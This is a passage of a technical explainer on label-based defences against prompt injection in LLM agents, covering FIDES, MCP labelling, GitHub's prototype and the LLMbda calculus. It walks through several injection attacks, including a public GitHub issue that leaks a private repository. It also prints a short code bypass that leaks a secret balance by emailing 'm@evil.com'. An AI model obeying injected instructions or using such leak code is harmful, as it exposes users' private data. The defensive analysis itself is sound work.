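When the emails arrive, FIDES compares their label with the conversation's. Adding them would make the conversation untrusted, so FIDES stores them in `#emails` and puts only that name in the conversation. The quarantined model writes the summary, and FIDES stores it in another variable, `#summary`. The planner's model then outputs a call to send `#summary` without having read its contents. Both the decision to send and the choice of recipient came from trusted text, so the loop fills in the summary and sends the message.

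The message itself is still untrusted. An email in the mailbox could contain an instruction to produce an empty or false summary, and the quarantined model might follow it. The strict form of the trusted-action policy also checks arguments, so it would refuse to send the message. The looser form guarantees that a stranger cannot choose the action or the recipient, but not that the summary is accurate.

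The strict form rules out a lot of ordinary work. *SPA* (2026) describes an agent that writes a plan and checks its labels before running it. Turning on the label checks reduced the share of AgentDojo tasks the agent completed from 53.0 to 29.0 per cent. The checks rejected about 53 per cent of its plans, typically because a plan passed one tool's untrusted output to another tool that required trusted arguments. Without the checks, only 4 of 949 attacks succeeded.

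Willison's design hides all untrusted content, whereas FIDES hides data only if it would make the conversation's label more restrictive. FIDES can do this field by field, so the planner's model may see an email's date while the body stays in a variable. The planner can also open a variable with a tool called `inspect`, but this adds the variable's contents and label to the conversation, which may prevent later tool calls.

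Willison called his solution "pretty bad". He expected it to make assistants harder to build and less pleasant to use, and he warned that one programming mistake could leak untrusted text to the privileged model. The quarantined model could also write a message that tricks the user into copying private data to an attacker's website.

### Limiting the answer's type

Hiding the data is enough when its contents don't affect which calls the agent needs to make. Costa and colleagues call such tasks data-independent. In a data-dependent task, the agent has to learn something from the data before it can choose a call. In their example, which is close to the one from Narisetty and colleagues, the agent has to read three emails and create a calendar event if any of them contains a meeting request.

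FIDES partly solves this problem by restricting the quarantined model's answer. The planner queries that model about whether there is a meeting request and specifies that the answer must be yes or no. It then inspects the answer and, if it is yes, has the quarantined model extract the details into a variable and passes that variable to the calendar tool. The planner's model receives only one bit of information from the untrusted emails, which is too little to carry an instruction.

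Constrained decoding can enforce the answer's type. Before the model writes each token, the software running it rules out every token that would break the required format. If the format allows only "true" and "false", the quarantined model cannot write anything else, whatever instructions the emails contain.

FIDES adds the data's type to its label. The types form their own lattice, ordered by how much information each can carry, from yes/no through a choice from a fixed list to free text. A policy can then accept an untrusted yes/no answer as grounds for creating a calendar event but reject untrusted free text. A yes/no answer carries at most 1 bit, and a choice among k options carries at most log₂ k bits, or 3 bits for eight options. Ten yes/no answers together can carry up to 10 bits, enough to distinguish 2¹⁰ = 1,024 cases, so a designer also has to consider how many questions the planner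 may ask.

Costa and colleagues did not use constrained decoding in their experiments, because they found it unnecessary for most AgentDojo tasks. Jacob, Alghamdi and colleagues (2025), in *Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation*, built and tested a similar idea. Their quarantined model may pass on only whole numbers, decimals, yes/no answers and choices from a fixed list. They compared agents with and without this restriction on three jobs:

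| Job and model | Tasks completed, unrestricted | Tasks completed, restricted | Attack success, unrestricted | Attack success, restricted |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Online shopping, GPT-4o | 21.8% | 22.4% | 31.7% | 0% |
| Scheduling meetings, GPT-4o | 90.0% | 91.0% | 63.0% | 0% |
| Fixing software bugs, GPT-5.2 | 68.3% | 45.0% | 98.9% | 0% |

The restriction did no harm where a few values captured everything that mattered. To schedule a meeting, the agent needs only the times the other person suggested, and it can receive those as choices from a list of slots. A bug report is harder to reduce to a few values. The quarantined model could pass on the type of bug, the file and the line numbers, but not the reporter's explanation of what went wrong. The researchers had to experiment a good deal before they found a format that worked.

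An answer of the right type can still be false. The shopping agent's quarantined model turns each customer review into two scores from 0 to 10, and a malicious reviewer could persuade it to give a bad product a 10. The agent uses the median score, so one such review has little effect, but many fake reviews would have more. *APPA* (Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues, 2026), a paper on a competing system, stresses that checking an answer's format does not make it true. In that system, a yes/no answer from untrusted text stays untrusted unless the people who set up the system explicitly decide otherwise. The system also rejects numbers of unlimited size, which could encode a whole sentence.

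Labels can also replace the rule that a quarantined model has no tools. In *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026), a second agent can read untrusted data and keep calling tools, because label checks stop any call that the data should not influence.

### What explicit secrecy guarantees

Costa and colleagues show that the labelled loop can enforce explicit secrecy, which means that an agent never copies secret data, or anything it computes from secret data, into a place that outsiders can see. Schoepe, Balliu and colleagues defined this property in *Explicit Secrecy* to state exactly what this kind of label tracking achieves.

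Take one run of the agent, up to any point, and let d₁ be the contents of its storage at the start. The steps that the agent performed amount to a function g, which turns the contents of the storage before the run into the contents afterwards. Now imagine different starting contents d₂, with the same public data as d₁ but different secrets. Write d₁ =ₗ d₂ to mean that their public parts match. The run satisfies explicit secrecy if, for every such d₂,

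g(d₁) =ₗ g(d₂).

In other words, if somebody changed the secrets and repeated exactly the same steps, the public data would come out the same.

The words "exactly the same steps" leave a gap. Schoepe and colleagues illustrate it with a short program in which h is secret and l is public:

```
if h = 0 then l := 1 else l := 2
output l
```

If h is 0, the program sets l to 1 and outputs it. Repeating those two steps with a different h would still output 1, so the run satisfies explicit secrecy. But anyone who reads the program and sees the output 1 knows that h is 0. This kind of leak, through the choice of steps, is called an implicit flow.

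An agent can leak in the same way. If it reads a private medical letter and then either books surgery or cancels an appointment, an observer who can see which tool it called learns something about the letter. Costa and colleagues accept this gap. Closing it requires a stronger property called noninterference, which they argue would stop an agent that had read anything secret from using almost any tool with publicly visible effects. Explicit secrecy also doesn't cover what an observer could work out from the timing of calls or the size of network packets, and its definition assumes that the model always gives the same response to the same input.

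Researchers disagree about how much information an attacker could extract through an agent's choice of tools. Costa and colleagues describe the leak as limited. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) objects that the guarantee is weakest where data and control are interchangeable, and that leaks through control can be made efficient there. Arithmetic supports the objection, since a choice among 16 visibly different tools reveals up to 4 bits, and 20 such choices could reveal 80 bits, enough for a ten-character password. Schoepe and colleagues argue that in ordinary software, ignoring implicit flows is riskiest when the code is malicious, because the attacker then decides which flows to use. An agent that obeys an injected instruction poses much the same risk.

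### Results on AgentDojo

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo in 2025 with OpenAI's GPT-4o and o1. For the security test they used GPT-4o and one of the benchmark's strongest fixed attacks, in which the attacker knows the names of the agent's tools. They compared FIDES with a basic planner and ran each with and without policy checks.

Without checks, 152 attacks succeeded against the basic planner and 21 against the FIDES planner. Hiding text in variables therefore stopped most attacks by itself, but the FIDES planner sometimes opened a variable and followed the instructions inside. With checks on, no attack succeeded against either planner.

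That last result depends on what counts as an attack. AgentDojo's scoring recorded three successful attacks on FIDES with checks on, all in Slack, but the researchers rejected all three after inspecting them. They give several reasons for overruling the benchmark in such cases. Sometimes AgentDojo counts an attack as successful when the agent requests a forbidden call, even though the policy stops the call. Sometimes the policy deliberately allows the attacker's goal, such as adding an event with no guests to the user's own calendar. Other attacks change only the text the user sees, for instance by making the assistant recommend a particular hotel. FIDES does not try to prevent these attacks, although they could harm the user.

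AgentDojo does not come with labels, so the researchers marked a field as untrusted if at least one of the benchmark's attacks used it. An organisation labelling its own data would not know the attacks in advance. The test shows that the checks work when the labels are right, but it gives little evidence of how often an organisation would get them right.

To measure the cost, the researchers counted the tasks each agent completed when nobody was attacking it. These are averages across AgentDojo's four environments:

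| Agent | GPT-4o | o1 |
|---|---|---|
| Basic planner, no checks | 84.3% | 84.0% |
| Basic planner, with checks | 41.9% | 44.4% |
| FIDES, no checks | 60.6% | 77.6% |
| FIDES, with checks | 50.0% | 60.8% |

With checks on, FIDES completed more tasks than the basic planner, by 8 percentage points with GPT-4o and 16 points with o1. Costa and colleagues also report that with checks off, the extra machinery lowered task completion by 6.3 points with o1 and by 23.7 points with GPT-4o, which often confused variable names or failed to use the quarantined model.

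A company deciding whether to adopt FIDES would probably care more about the difference between an unprotected agent and FIDES with its checks on. That difference was about 34 points with GPT-4o and 23 with o1.

Much of the loss came from data-dependent tasks, which made up more than 40 per cent of tasks in the banking and Slack environments but at most 10 per cent in the other two. Many banking tasks require the agent to open a file and follow the instructions in it. FIDES blocks these on purpose, since an agent that follows instructions in an untrusted file is open to prompt injection. In the travel environment, the basic planner did better than FIDES even with checks on, because the policies let many travel tools run after the agent had read untrusted text.

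The agent completed some tasks by luck. In one, the user asked it to change a password if there had been a suspicious transaction. The transaction descriptions were hidden in variables. The agent saw one large amount, judged it suspicious and changed the password without checking the description. AgentDojo scored this as a success.

Kravchenko and colleagues left AgentDojo out of their 2026 evaluation because current models resist its injections without any defence. They used two other benchmarks to compare APPA with two configurations based on the FIDES mechanisms in Microsoft's Agent Framework, a toolkit for developers. When prompts on one benchmark encouraged the models to follow instructions embedded in data, attacks succeeded between 5.0 and 30.8 per cent of the time against the FIDES configurations and never against APPA.

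This does not refute the guarantee, because the policies in those configurations did not cover everything the benchmarks tested. One policy, for example, did not check data passed from the agent's stored memory to the user. The researchers also chose the configurations themselves and had a competing system to promote. Even so, the result shows how easily a system with a sound mechanism can end up with an incomplete policy.

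### Planning around the policies

In *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), a group that includes most of the FIDES team, argue that comparing FIDES's scores with those of an unprotected agent is unfair, because companies do not usually let unprotected agents act freely. GitHub Copilot Chat, for example, reads data without asking in the code editor Visual Studio Code, but it asks the user to approve other tool calls. In practice, the unprotected agent could therefore reach its high score only if someone were available to approve everything.

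They propose counting the approvals. An ordinary agent needs one for every consequential call, while an agent with labels needs one only when a call fails its policy check. Their main measures are the total number of approvals across completed tasks and the share of tasks an agent completes with at most k approvals, where k = 0 means the agent works alone.

They also built a new agent, Prudentia, on top of FIDES. The planner in FIDES has no access to the policies, so it may open a variable unnecessarily and lose the ability to send a message. Prudentia's planner has access to the policy for each tool and the label on its own conversation. Before it opens a variable, it is instructed to explain why it needs to and to list the calls it expects to make afterwards.

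Prudentia can also ask the user to endorse a piece of data, which means declaring it trusted. Suppose an email lists ten tasks, each requiring a consequential call. If the agent reads the email without this endorsement, the conversation becomes untrusted and the user has to approve all ten calls. If the user endorses the email first, the agent can make the calls without asking again.

The researchers ran four agents on AgentDojo and measured the share of tasks that each completed with no approvals at all:

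| Model | Ordinary agent | Basic planner with labels | FIDES | Prudentia |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 28.0% | 38.4% | 50.3% | 42.5% |
| o3-mini | 24.3% | 35.5% | 50.1% | 59.1% |
| o4-mini | 32.8% | 42.5% | 53.2% | 59.4% |
| GPT-5 | 35.1% | 43.4% | 57.1% | 72.7% |

By this measure, labels make an agent more useful. With GPT-5, Prudentia completed more than twice as many tasks alone as the ordinary agent did. It needed an average of 7.3 approvals across the whole benchmark, compared with 41.3 for FIDES and 52.0 for the ordinary agent. With unlimited approvals, Prudentia completed 80.0 per cent of tasks and the ordinary agent 72.3 per cent. The exception was GPT-4o, which is not a reasoning model and did better with FIDES than with Prudentia's more complicated instructions.

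On WASP, a benchmark for agents that use a web browser, injections diverted the ordinary agent in 14.6 to 61.1 per cent of cases, depending on the model and the website. None diverted Prudentia, and it needed no approvals. However, WASP is an easy case for this design because its user tasks are posting a comment and upvoting a post, so the agent never needs to read what strangers have written.

Prudentia's planning is expensive. With GPT-4o, an average AgentDojo task cost 3.9 to 6.3 US cents, compared with 1.5 to 3.3 cents for FIDES and 0.4 to 1.1 cents for the basic planner with labels. Kolluri and colleagues had not tried to reduce the cost and expect it could fall considerably.

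No people took part in these experiments. The researchers counted the points at which an agent would have needed approval, and assumed that users would approve legitimate requests and stop malicious ones. Real users may not read the requests carefully, although they are more likely to read seven than fifty. A mistaken endorsement can also do more harm than a mistaken approval of a call, which permits only one bad action. If a user endorses an email that contains a hidden instruction, the instruction is trusted as much as the user's own request, and the policy checks no longer treat the calls it causes as untrusted.

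## Passing labels between a tool server and an agent: GitHub and the Model Context Protocol

In the FIDES experiments, the researchers labelled every tool's data themselves. Outside a benchmark, an agent often uses tools run by another organisation, which usually knows more about the data than the agent's developer does. GitHub records which code repositories are private and who wrote each comment, while the developer would have to infer this from the returned text. If GitHub doesn't send its labels with the data, the agent receives plain text without the labels its policy checks need.

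### How agents reach tools run by others

The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is a shared standard for connecting agents to tools. A server offers the tools, and a client is the software that runs the agent. They communicate in four steps:

1. The client requests the server's list of tools. For each tool, the server returns a name, a description in plain language and a schema that specifies the arguments.
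2. The model reads the descriptions and picks a tool.
3. The client sends the call to the server, which runs the tool and returns the result.
4. The client passes the result to the model.

A server can also attach annotations to a tool. These include four yes/no hints about whether the tool only reads data, whether it can destroy anything, whether repeating a call is safe, and whether it reaches an "open world" of outside parties. The current specification, Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), requires clients to treat annotations as untrusted unless they come from a trusted server.

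Annotations describe a tool, so they can't replace labels on data. A tool that reads GitHub issues has the same annotations whether an issue comes from a public repository or a private one. In *Attested Tool-Server Admission*, Metere (2026) argues that MCP standardises messages but not trust. The client reads the server's own description of its tools, and the protocol provides no way to specify which servers the client may use or how sensitive the data it sends them may be.

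Since July 2026, MCP has had no sessions, so a server cannot assume that two calls belong to the same conversation. If a server needs to remember something, such as a shopping basket, it returns an identifier for the client to send back later. According to the specification, this identifier is a name and not a capability, so a server with user accounts should check the caller's authorization on every call. The server also has no record of what the agent has read elsewhere, so the client must send that information as labels with each call.

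### Labels and policies in the metadata

Microsoft's *Information-flow control* describes a prototype, built partly with GitHub, that sends labels in `_meta`, a field that MCP reserves for extra information. Clients that don't support the labels can ignore them and work as before.

Each label applies to a particular part of a call or result. A call that posts a message to a Microsoft Teams channel might look like this in simplified form:

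```
tool:       SendMessageToChannel
arguments:  channelId, content
labels:     $                     untrusted, public
            $.arguments.content   trusted, readers {Alex, Priya}
```

The `$` stands for the whole call. Its label records that the agent had read something untrusted before making the call. The message text has its own label, which allows only Alex and Priya to read the text. Any part without its own label takes one from the part that contains it or from the parts inside it.

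The server also publishes a policy for each tool, in the `_meta` field of its tool list. Before each call, the client evaluates the policy, which returns one of three decisions: allow the call, deny it, or ask a person. A policy can first look up facts by calling the server's read-only tools. In Microsoft's example for Teams, it fetches the list of channel members. If M is the set of members and R the set of people who may read the message, the policy works as follows:

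- If the conversation is trusted, allow the call.
- If the conversation is untrusted but M − R is empty, allow the call, because every member may already read the message.
- Otherwise, ask the user and list the people in M − R.

The first rule is the robust declassification that FIDES uses. The second covers only the people in the channel at the time of the call, so someone who joins later may still see the message.

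Together, these arrangements form an interface contract in each direction. The server assumes that the labels on a call cover everything that influenced it, and guarantees that the labels on the result cover everything that influenced the result, including any outside source the tool consulted. The client assumes that those labels and the published policy are correct, and guarantees that it will carry the labels into later calls and make no call that the policy forbids.

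The client has to run the check before it makes the call, because the call sends the arguments to the server, whose operator may not be allowed to see them. The server has to keep the labels on anything it stores. If an agent saves private text in an online notebook that discards labels, the text will be unlabeled, and therefore unprotected, when the agent fetches it again.

### A public issue and a private repository

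On GitHub, anyone can open an issue, which is a bug report or request, in a public repository. Microsoft gives an example based on an attack that researchers demonstrated in 2025. A stranger opens an issue in a public repository, asking for information from a private one, `contoso/core`, to be posted as a comment. Alex, a user with access to both repositories, tells his agent to deal with the issue.

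| Step | Label on the new data | Label on the conversation afterwards |
|---|---|---|
| Alex makes his request | trusted, public | trusted, public |
| The agent reads the issue | untrusted, public | untrusted, public |
| The agent reads a file in `contoso/core` | trusted, private | untrusted, private |
| The agent tries to post a public comment | none, because the client refuses the call | untrusted, private |

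The agent may read the private file even after the stranger's text has influenced it, because reading the file reveals nothing to the stranger. The policy forbids only the last step, posting publicly when the conversation contains both untrusted and private data. If the agent had worked only in public repositories, or only in private ones, it could have finished without interruption. The policy would not prevent a stranger's issue from causing the agent to post a false or abusive comment if the agent had read nothing private.

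Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) describes a stricter version, in which the attacker wants the contents of `.env`, a file where programmers often keep passwords. The comment tool accepts only public data, so the software blocks the comment whether or not the conversation is trusted. A separate rule on the file-writing tool rejects any call influenced by untrusted text, in case the hidden instruction is to overwrite a file.

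In July 2026, the security company Noma demonstrated a leak of this kind, which it named GitLost. The attack targeted GitHub Agentic Workflows, a feature that runs agents on routine repository tasks. According to SiliconANGLE's *‘GitLost’ vulnerability let GitHub’s AI workflows leak private repositories* (2026), an attacker without credentials could trigger the leak by posting just one crafted issue in a public repository. Expert Insights' *Researchers Trick Misconfigured GitHub AI Agent Into Leaking a Private Repo* (2026) stresses that the workflow was misconfigured.

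Agentic Workflows does use labels, as GitHub Next's *Control what your agentic workflows see with integrity filtering* explains, but it enforces them only for integrity. A maintainer sets a minimum level of trust, and the software removes anything below that level before the agent can read it. At the "approved" level, the agent sees text from the project's owners, members and collaborators, plus anything they have endorsed, for example with a thumbs-up. This would hide a stranger's issue, but an agent that sorts incoming bug reports has to read what strangers write, so its maintainer has to set a lower level. GitHub Next acknowledges that the software tracks confidentiality without acting on it, and so cannot prevent leaks between repositories.

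### A leak without an attacker

Labels also catch mistakes that involve no malicious text. In Microsoft's second example, Alex asks an agent to handle the unanswered emails in his inbox. Priya has sent him a preview of the quarterly sales figures. He also has an email from Marco, who is curious about the figures but isn't authorised to see them yet.

Each email's label lists the people who may read it. Priya's email has {Alex, Priya}, and Marco's has {Alex, Marco}. Once the agent has read both, anything it writes may draw on both, so its label is

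{Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}.

Marco is not in the resulting set, so the agent cannot reply to him unless Alex approves. If Priya had copied Marco on her email, its label would have been {Alex, Priya, Marco}. The intersection would then be {Alex, Marco}, and the reply could go out without approval.

The rule is cautious in ways that would annoy Alex. The set {Alex} excludes Priya too, so the agent would need approval even to thank her for her own figures. The need for approval also depends on the order of work. If the agent answered Marco before opening Priya's email, it could send the reply without approval, because the label would still be {Alex, Marco}. A developer could avoid many approvals by starting a fresh conversation for each email, but then the agent couldn't connect one email with another.

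The result also depends on the integrity labels. Under a policy like the one for Teams, an agent in a trusted conversation may release anything. If Alex's company labelled all internal email as trusted, that policy would allow the agent to send Marco the figures. To prevent accidents like this, the policy has to check the readers even when the conversation is trusted.

*MCPHunt* (Li, Sun and colleagues, 2026), a benchmark for agents connected to several MCP servers, describes the same problem with passwords and other credentials. An agent that uses its tools as intended can carry a credential from one server to another, even though each permission to read or write looks harmless by itself.

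### What has shipped

Developers can try most of the prototype, but all of it is optional or experimental.

| Software | What it does with labels | State |
|---|---|---|
| GitHub's MCP server | Attaches one label to each result from supported tools | Off unless the client's configuration turns it on |
| GitHub Copilot CLI, a coding agent for the command line | Tracks the conversation's label and enforces built-in policies for selected GitHub tools | Behind an experimental flag, with no support for other servers |
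| Microsoft Agent Framework, a toolkit for building agents | Tracks labels, enforces policies and can hide untrusted text behind a quarantined model | Experimental module, announced on 20 May 2026 |
| Microsoft's labelling gateway | Adds labels and policies to servers that have none | Open-source prototype covering selected tools |

GitHub's labels are defined in the package *ifc* (2026). At first, in version 1.0.5, released on 18 May 2026, they covered only the user's own profile, file contents, lists of issues and search results. By version 1.3.0, GitHub had added workflow logs, releases, security alerts and several other kinds of data. Labelling some of these correctly requires detailed knowledge of GitHub. A draft release, for instance, is private even in a public repository.

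Microsoft describes both files and issues from private repositories as trusted. The documentation for *ifc* agrees about files, because only collaborators can change them, but treats the text of issues as untrusted in all repositories. This is safer, since a collaborator may paste text from a customer's email into a private issue.

A common standard is still some way off, and until there is one, the labels work only in clients whose developers have written code to read them. GitHub and OpenAI staff have drafted a proposal, SEP-1913, to add trust and sensitivity markings to MCP. According to a summary in the discussion of Model Context Protocol's *SEP-1862*, SEP-1913 would let a server mark individual items in a mixed result, and it includes rules for carrying the markings through a session. Model Context Protocol's *Tool Annotations Charter* listed the proposal as a draft in April 2026 and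 allowed the group discussing it only to make recommendations. The group lists as an open question whether tool results should carry annotations at all. In July, GitHub (2026) announced that its server supported the new version of MCP, but that version has no standard field for these labels. Microsoft plans to work with the MCP community on a proposal for labels and policies.

### When a label is missing

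Agent Framework treats data from an unlabelled tool as trusted and public, the least restrictive label. Suppose a developer adds a tool that fetches web pages and forgets to label it. A page containing a hidden instruction to overwrite a file then enters the conversation as trusted text. If the agent has read nothing labelled untrusted, the check on the file-writing tool passes without a warning. Microsoft lists this first among the module's limitations.

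This default goes against Saltzer and Schroeder's principle of denying access unless somebody has explicitly permitted it. MCP's own annotations follow that principle. A client should assume that a tool with no annotations can change and destroy things and reach the outside world, according to a March post on the protocol's blog (Model Context Protocol, 2026).

A missing label is especially risky when different organisations write the server and the client. If a server cannot determine whether a repository is private, its developers may reasonably choose to omit the label rather than guess. A client that reads a missing label as "trusted and public" will then allow the result to be shared even though it may be private.

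The safer default would be to treat unlabelled data as untrusted and private, though this would mainly hinder the use of harmless tools. An unlabelled clock could make the conversation untrusted and private by returning the time, and the agent would then need approval to write a file or post a public comment. The FIDES results give some idea of the scale, since policy checks roughly halved the share of tasks that the basic planner completed, even though the researchers had marked only some fields as untrusted. Hiding unlabelled results in variables would let the agent complete some of the blocked tasks, but the agent would need an extra model call whenever it had to use their contents.

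Developers could avoid most of this by labelling their tools, but labelling takes work. IBM Research notes that information-flow control systems typically rely on labels that people write by hand. For each tool on a new server, Microsoft's gateway needs a schema for the results, a function that computes their labels, and a policy, which can be a built-in one.

The stricter default seems worth the trouble for an agent that can spend money or publish data, because a developer will notice blocked work sooner than a missing label. Microsoft asked developers in its May 2026 announcement whether a stricter default would suit their agents.

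### Lasting restrictions and vague approvals

Once a stranger's issue enters the conversation in Agent Framework, everything afterwards counts as untrusted unless the developer explicitly removes the issue. GitHub adds to the problem by giving each result a single label, so if a search matches nine public repositories and one private repository, the whole result is labeled private.

Microsoft is considering labels that apply to individual messages, or that fade when the software condenses a long conversation. Both ideas need care, because a text can still influence the model's work after it is deleted. If the model writes a plan based on a malicious issue, and the software then removes the issue but keeps the plan, the attacker's instruction may survive in the plan under a trusted label. A summary of the conversation can preserve the instruction in the same way, so it needs the labels of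 everything that went into it. To lift the restriction safely, the software would have to discard both the issue and everything the model wrote after reading it.

When a call breaks a policy, Agent Framework can ask the user for approval. The request names the tool and the label that caused the block, which may not be enough for a good decision. A user who learns only that the conversation is "private" has to work out which file made it private and who would see the comment. The request in the example policy for Teams is more useful because it lists the people who would gain access. If Alex saw that a reply would show the sales figures to Marco, he could decide at once.

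### Labels from a server the client does not control

A client takes on little extra risk by relying on GitHub to label its own data, because GitHub already stores the repositories and decides who can read them. Relying on an unfamiliar server is riskier. Its operator could label a stranger's text as trusted, or publish a policy that allows every call and then collect whatever the agent sends.

One of Microsoft's shortcuts, meant to spare developers from writing policies, would be especially exposed to this. A client could use MCP's existing annotations and always allow calls to tools annotated as only reading data and not reaching the outside world. A dishonest operator could then receive private data by setting those two annotations falsely. The Model Context Protocol blog warns against relying on annotations this way. It distinguishes hints, which remain useful if some servers get them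 wrong, from contracts, which have to be true. It leaves contracts to other parts of the system, such as the authorization layer. By that distinction, the prototype's labels and policies are contracts.

Honest operators make mistakes too. *ACaM* (Santra, Kirat and colleagues, 2026) cites research that found mismatches between the descriptions of MCP tools and their code in 10 to 13 per cent of cases. The paper gives the example of a weather tool that returns a correct forecast but also reads a credentials file and sends it to an outside server. A label on the forecast would not reveal this, because the leak happens inside the tool.

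Santra and colleagues therefore work out what a tool can do from its source code. Their method cannot examine a remote server whose code is unavailable, as is usual when another company runs the tools. Microsoft's *MCP Security Gateway* describes a more limited check, in which the client stores a cryptographic fingerprint of each tool's description and schema and later checks that they still match it. This detects changes to the description or schema, but misses changes to the code that leave both the same.

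The people who run the agent can also do the labelling. GitHub Next uses programs called guards, each written to label the data from one source. A small reference monitor then compares the labels without interpreting them. Somebody has to write a guard for every source, but the server's operator no longer decides how far the agent trusts the data.

A client can combine the two approaches by giving each server a label of its own and joining it with whatever label the server sends:

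label used = client's label for the server ⊔ label sent by the server.

A join never makes a label less restrictive, so false labels from the server could block legitimate work but could not loosen the client's own rules. Santra and colleagues' analysis likewise lets a language model raise the sensitivity of a piece of data but never lower it. The client would have to treat policies the same way, applying both its own and the server's and following the stricter decision.

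The drawback is that when an honest but unfamiliar server labels its data as trusted, the label has no effect, because the client's own label overrides it. Somebody still has to decide which servers should get a looser label. Metere proposes extending MCP so that a client admits a server only after a security check. The idea came from the need to connect an agent safely to Google's servers for Gmail, Calendar and Drive.

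## A machine-checked proof for an agent program: the LLMbda calculus

Labels protect data only if the software updates them correctly at every step, and programmers easily get this wrong. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, designed LLMbda, a small programming language for agents, and proved that its labels account for everything that influences a program's results. The one exception is whether the program finishes. A computer checked the proof. The paper is the July version of *The LLMbda Calculus*, which first appeared in February.

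### A leak through a branch that does not run

The paper's main example of faulty tracking is CaMeL, an agent design in which a privileged model writes a program to carry out the user's request and a quarantined model reads the untrusted text. An interpreter runs the program, labels its values and checks the labels before each tool call. Suppose an attacker wants to know whether a customer's balance is above some threshold, and gets this line into the program:

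```
if balance > threshold: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

CaMeL blocks the email, because the decision to send it depended on a secret. The attacker can get round the block with two extra variables:

```
tmp = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

When a program tests a secret and then changes a variable, CaMeL marks that variable as secret. It does this only for changes the program actually makes:

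| | Balance above the threshold | Balance not above it |
|---|---|---|
| `tmp` after the first test | False, secret | True, public |
| `rich` after the second test | True, public | False, public |
| Email | goes out | does not go out |

The last line tests only `rich`, which is public in both cases, so the interpreter allows the email. The attacker receives it exactly when the balance is above the threshold. Computer scientists have known about this kind of leak, called an implicit flow, since the 1970s. Dongol (2026), in *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection*, proved that a similar leak occurs in one example agent that tracks labels through data but not through branches. The agent sends the attacker a 1 or a 0, both public constants, depending on the user's private notes.

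The usual remedy, which LLMbda adopts, is to stop a program that has tested a secret and is about to change something public. In the example, the program would stop at `tmp = False`. An observer can still learn one bit from whether the program stopped, which is tolerable if nobody can run it repeatedly.

CaMeL's interpreter sits inside an ordinary Python loop that starts another attempt after a failure and doesn't track labels, so an attacker could learn one bit from each attempt. By halving the possible range each time, the attacker could find a balance of up to about a million pounds, to the nearest pound, in twenty attempts. *Language-Based Agent Control* therefore requires developers to write the retry logic, and all the other code around the model, in the same checked language as the agent's own programs.

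### Three operations on a conversation

LLMbda extends the lambda calculus, a minimal language in which programs consist of functions. For example, `\x. x + 1` is the function that adds one to a number. The new language has three operations for working with a model:

- `@p` sends the prompt `p` to the model and returns the response. If the response is code, LLMbda runs it.
- `fork e` runs `e` in a temporary copy of the conversation and then returns to the original.
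- `clear` empties the conversation.

In the paper's basic examples, a label can contain U for untrusted, S for secret, both or neither. As in FIDES, the conversation has its own label, which passes to the model's response. In LLMbda, it also passes to anything that code in the response computes.

A developer can write a quarantined model in three lines:

```
let quarantine = \question.
  let reply = fork (let _ = clear in @question) in
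  reply.[1]
```

The function copies the conversation, empties the copy, asks the question there and returns the answer. The last line is needed because `@` returns a pair, with the answer in second place. Here is a simplified program that uses the function to reply to a stranger's email:

```
let category = quarantine ("Billing, support or general? " + email) in
send_email "bob@example.com" category "Acknowledged."
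```

The email carries the label U, so the temporary conversation and the category get that label too. The main conversation stays trusted because the email never entered it. But `send_email` requires a trusted subject line, so it stops the program when given the category as the subject.

CaMeL and FIDES build the separation between the two models into their architecture. In LLMbda, the separation is part of the program, so a developer can rearrange it without changing the interpreter.

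### Noninterference for programs that use chance

Garby and colleagues proved a version of noninterference, a property that Joseph Goguen and José Meseguer introduced in 1982. A program has this property if changing the data an observer may not see never changes the results the observer can see. For confidentiality, this means that changing a secret does not change the public results. For integrity, it means that changing untrusted text does not change the trusted results, so a stranger cannot influence anything the program labels as trusted.

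Noninterference is a stronger guarantee than the explicit secrecy in FIDES. It also rules out leaks through branches, because it accounts for the program taking different steps on different inputs.

A language model can answer the same prompt differently each time, so the definition has to compare probabilities. Let a and b be two starting states that look the same to an observer, and let μₐ and μ_b be the probabilities of each result that the observer might see. Ordinary probabilistic noninterference requires

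μₐ = μ_b.

LLMbda cannot meet this requirement, because its rule against changing public data may stop one run and allow the other. Some of the probability is then missing from the results. Suppose a program behaves like this:

| | Prints "heads" | Prints "tails" | Never finishes |
|---|---|---|---|
| Secret is A | 50% | 50% | 0% |
| Secret is B | 50% | 0% | 50% |

The secret's only effect is that, with secret B, runs that would have printed "tails" never finish. A definition that ignores whether a program finishes should accept this program. Garby and colleagues first tried comparing only the runs that finish, but the program then appears to leak the secret, because "heads" makes up half of the finished runs for secret A and all of them for secret B.

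They settled on a different test. It asks whether some list of probabilities ω, adding up to at most 1, is at least as large as both μₐ and μ_b for every result:

μₐ ≤ ω and μ_b ≤ ω.

In the example, an ω that assigns 50 per cent to each word works. If one secret gave 70 per cent heads and 30 per cent tails, and the other gave the reverse, ω would have to assign at least 70 per cent to each word. That adds up to 140 per cent, so the program would fail the test.

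The definition also limits how much an observer can learn. The statistical distance between μₐ and μ_b, which is half the sum of their differences, is at most the average probability of not finishing. In the example, both are 25 per cent. If a program always finishes, the two sets of probabilities must be identical.

### A theorem about every program

The main theorem is that every LLMbda program passes this test for every observer. To prove it, Garby and colleagues defined a second way of running programs, which skips a step as soon as its label hides it from the observer and returns a blank value instead. Every visible result is at least as likely under this method as under the real one. The method also gives the same probabilities for any two inputs that look alike to the observer, because it never uses the data in which they differ. Those probabilities therefore serve as ω.

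The theorem applies to programs that a model writes during a run, whatever they contain. If a stranger's email causes the model to reply with malicious code, that code runs with the email's untrusted label and cannot remove it. FIDES has a noninterference theorem too, but only for one planning loop. A developer can change the tools in that loop without affecting the proof, but would need a new proof after adding a retry loop or a second agent. CaMeL can run whatever program its model writes, but it has no comparable theorem.

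Correct labels don't stop an attack by themselves. In one of the paper's examples, a user asks an agent to send a reminder about a meeting. The agent reads an email containing a hidden request to cancel and sends a cancellation instead. The theorem still holds, because the cancellation carries the label U, but the email tool doesn't check labels. When the tool accepts only trusted subject lines and message text, and the program is written before the agent reads the email, the agent sends the reminder.

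### Endorsement

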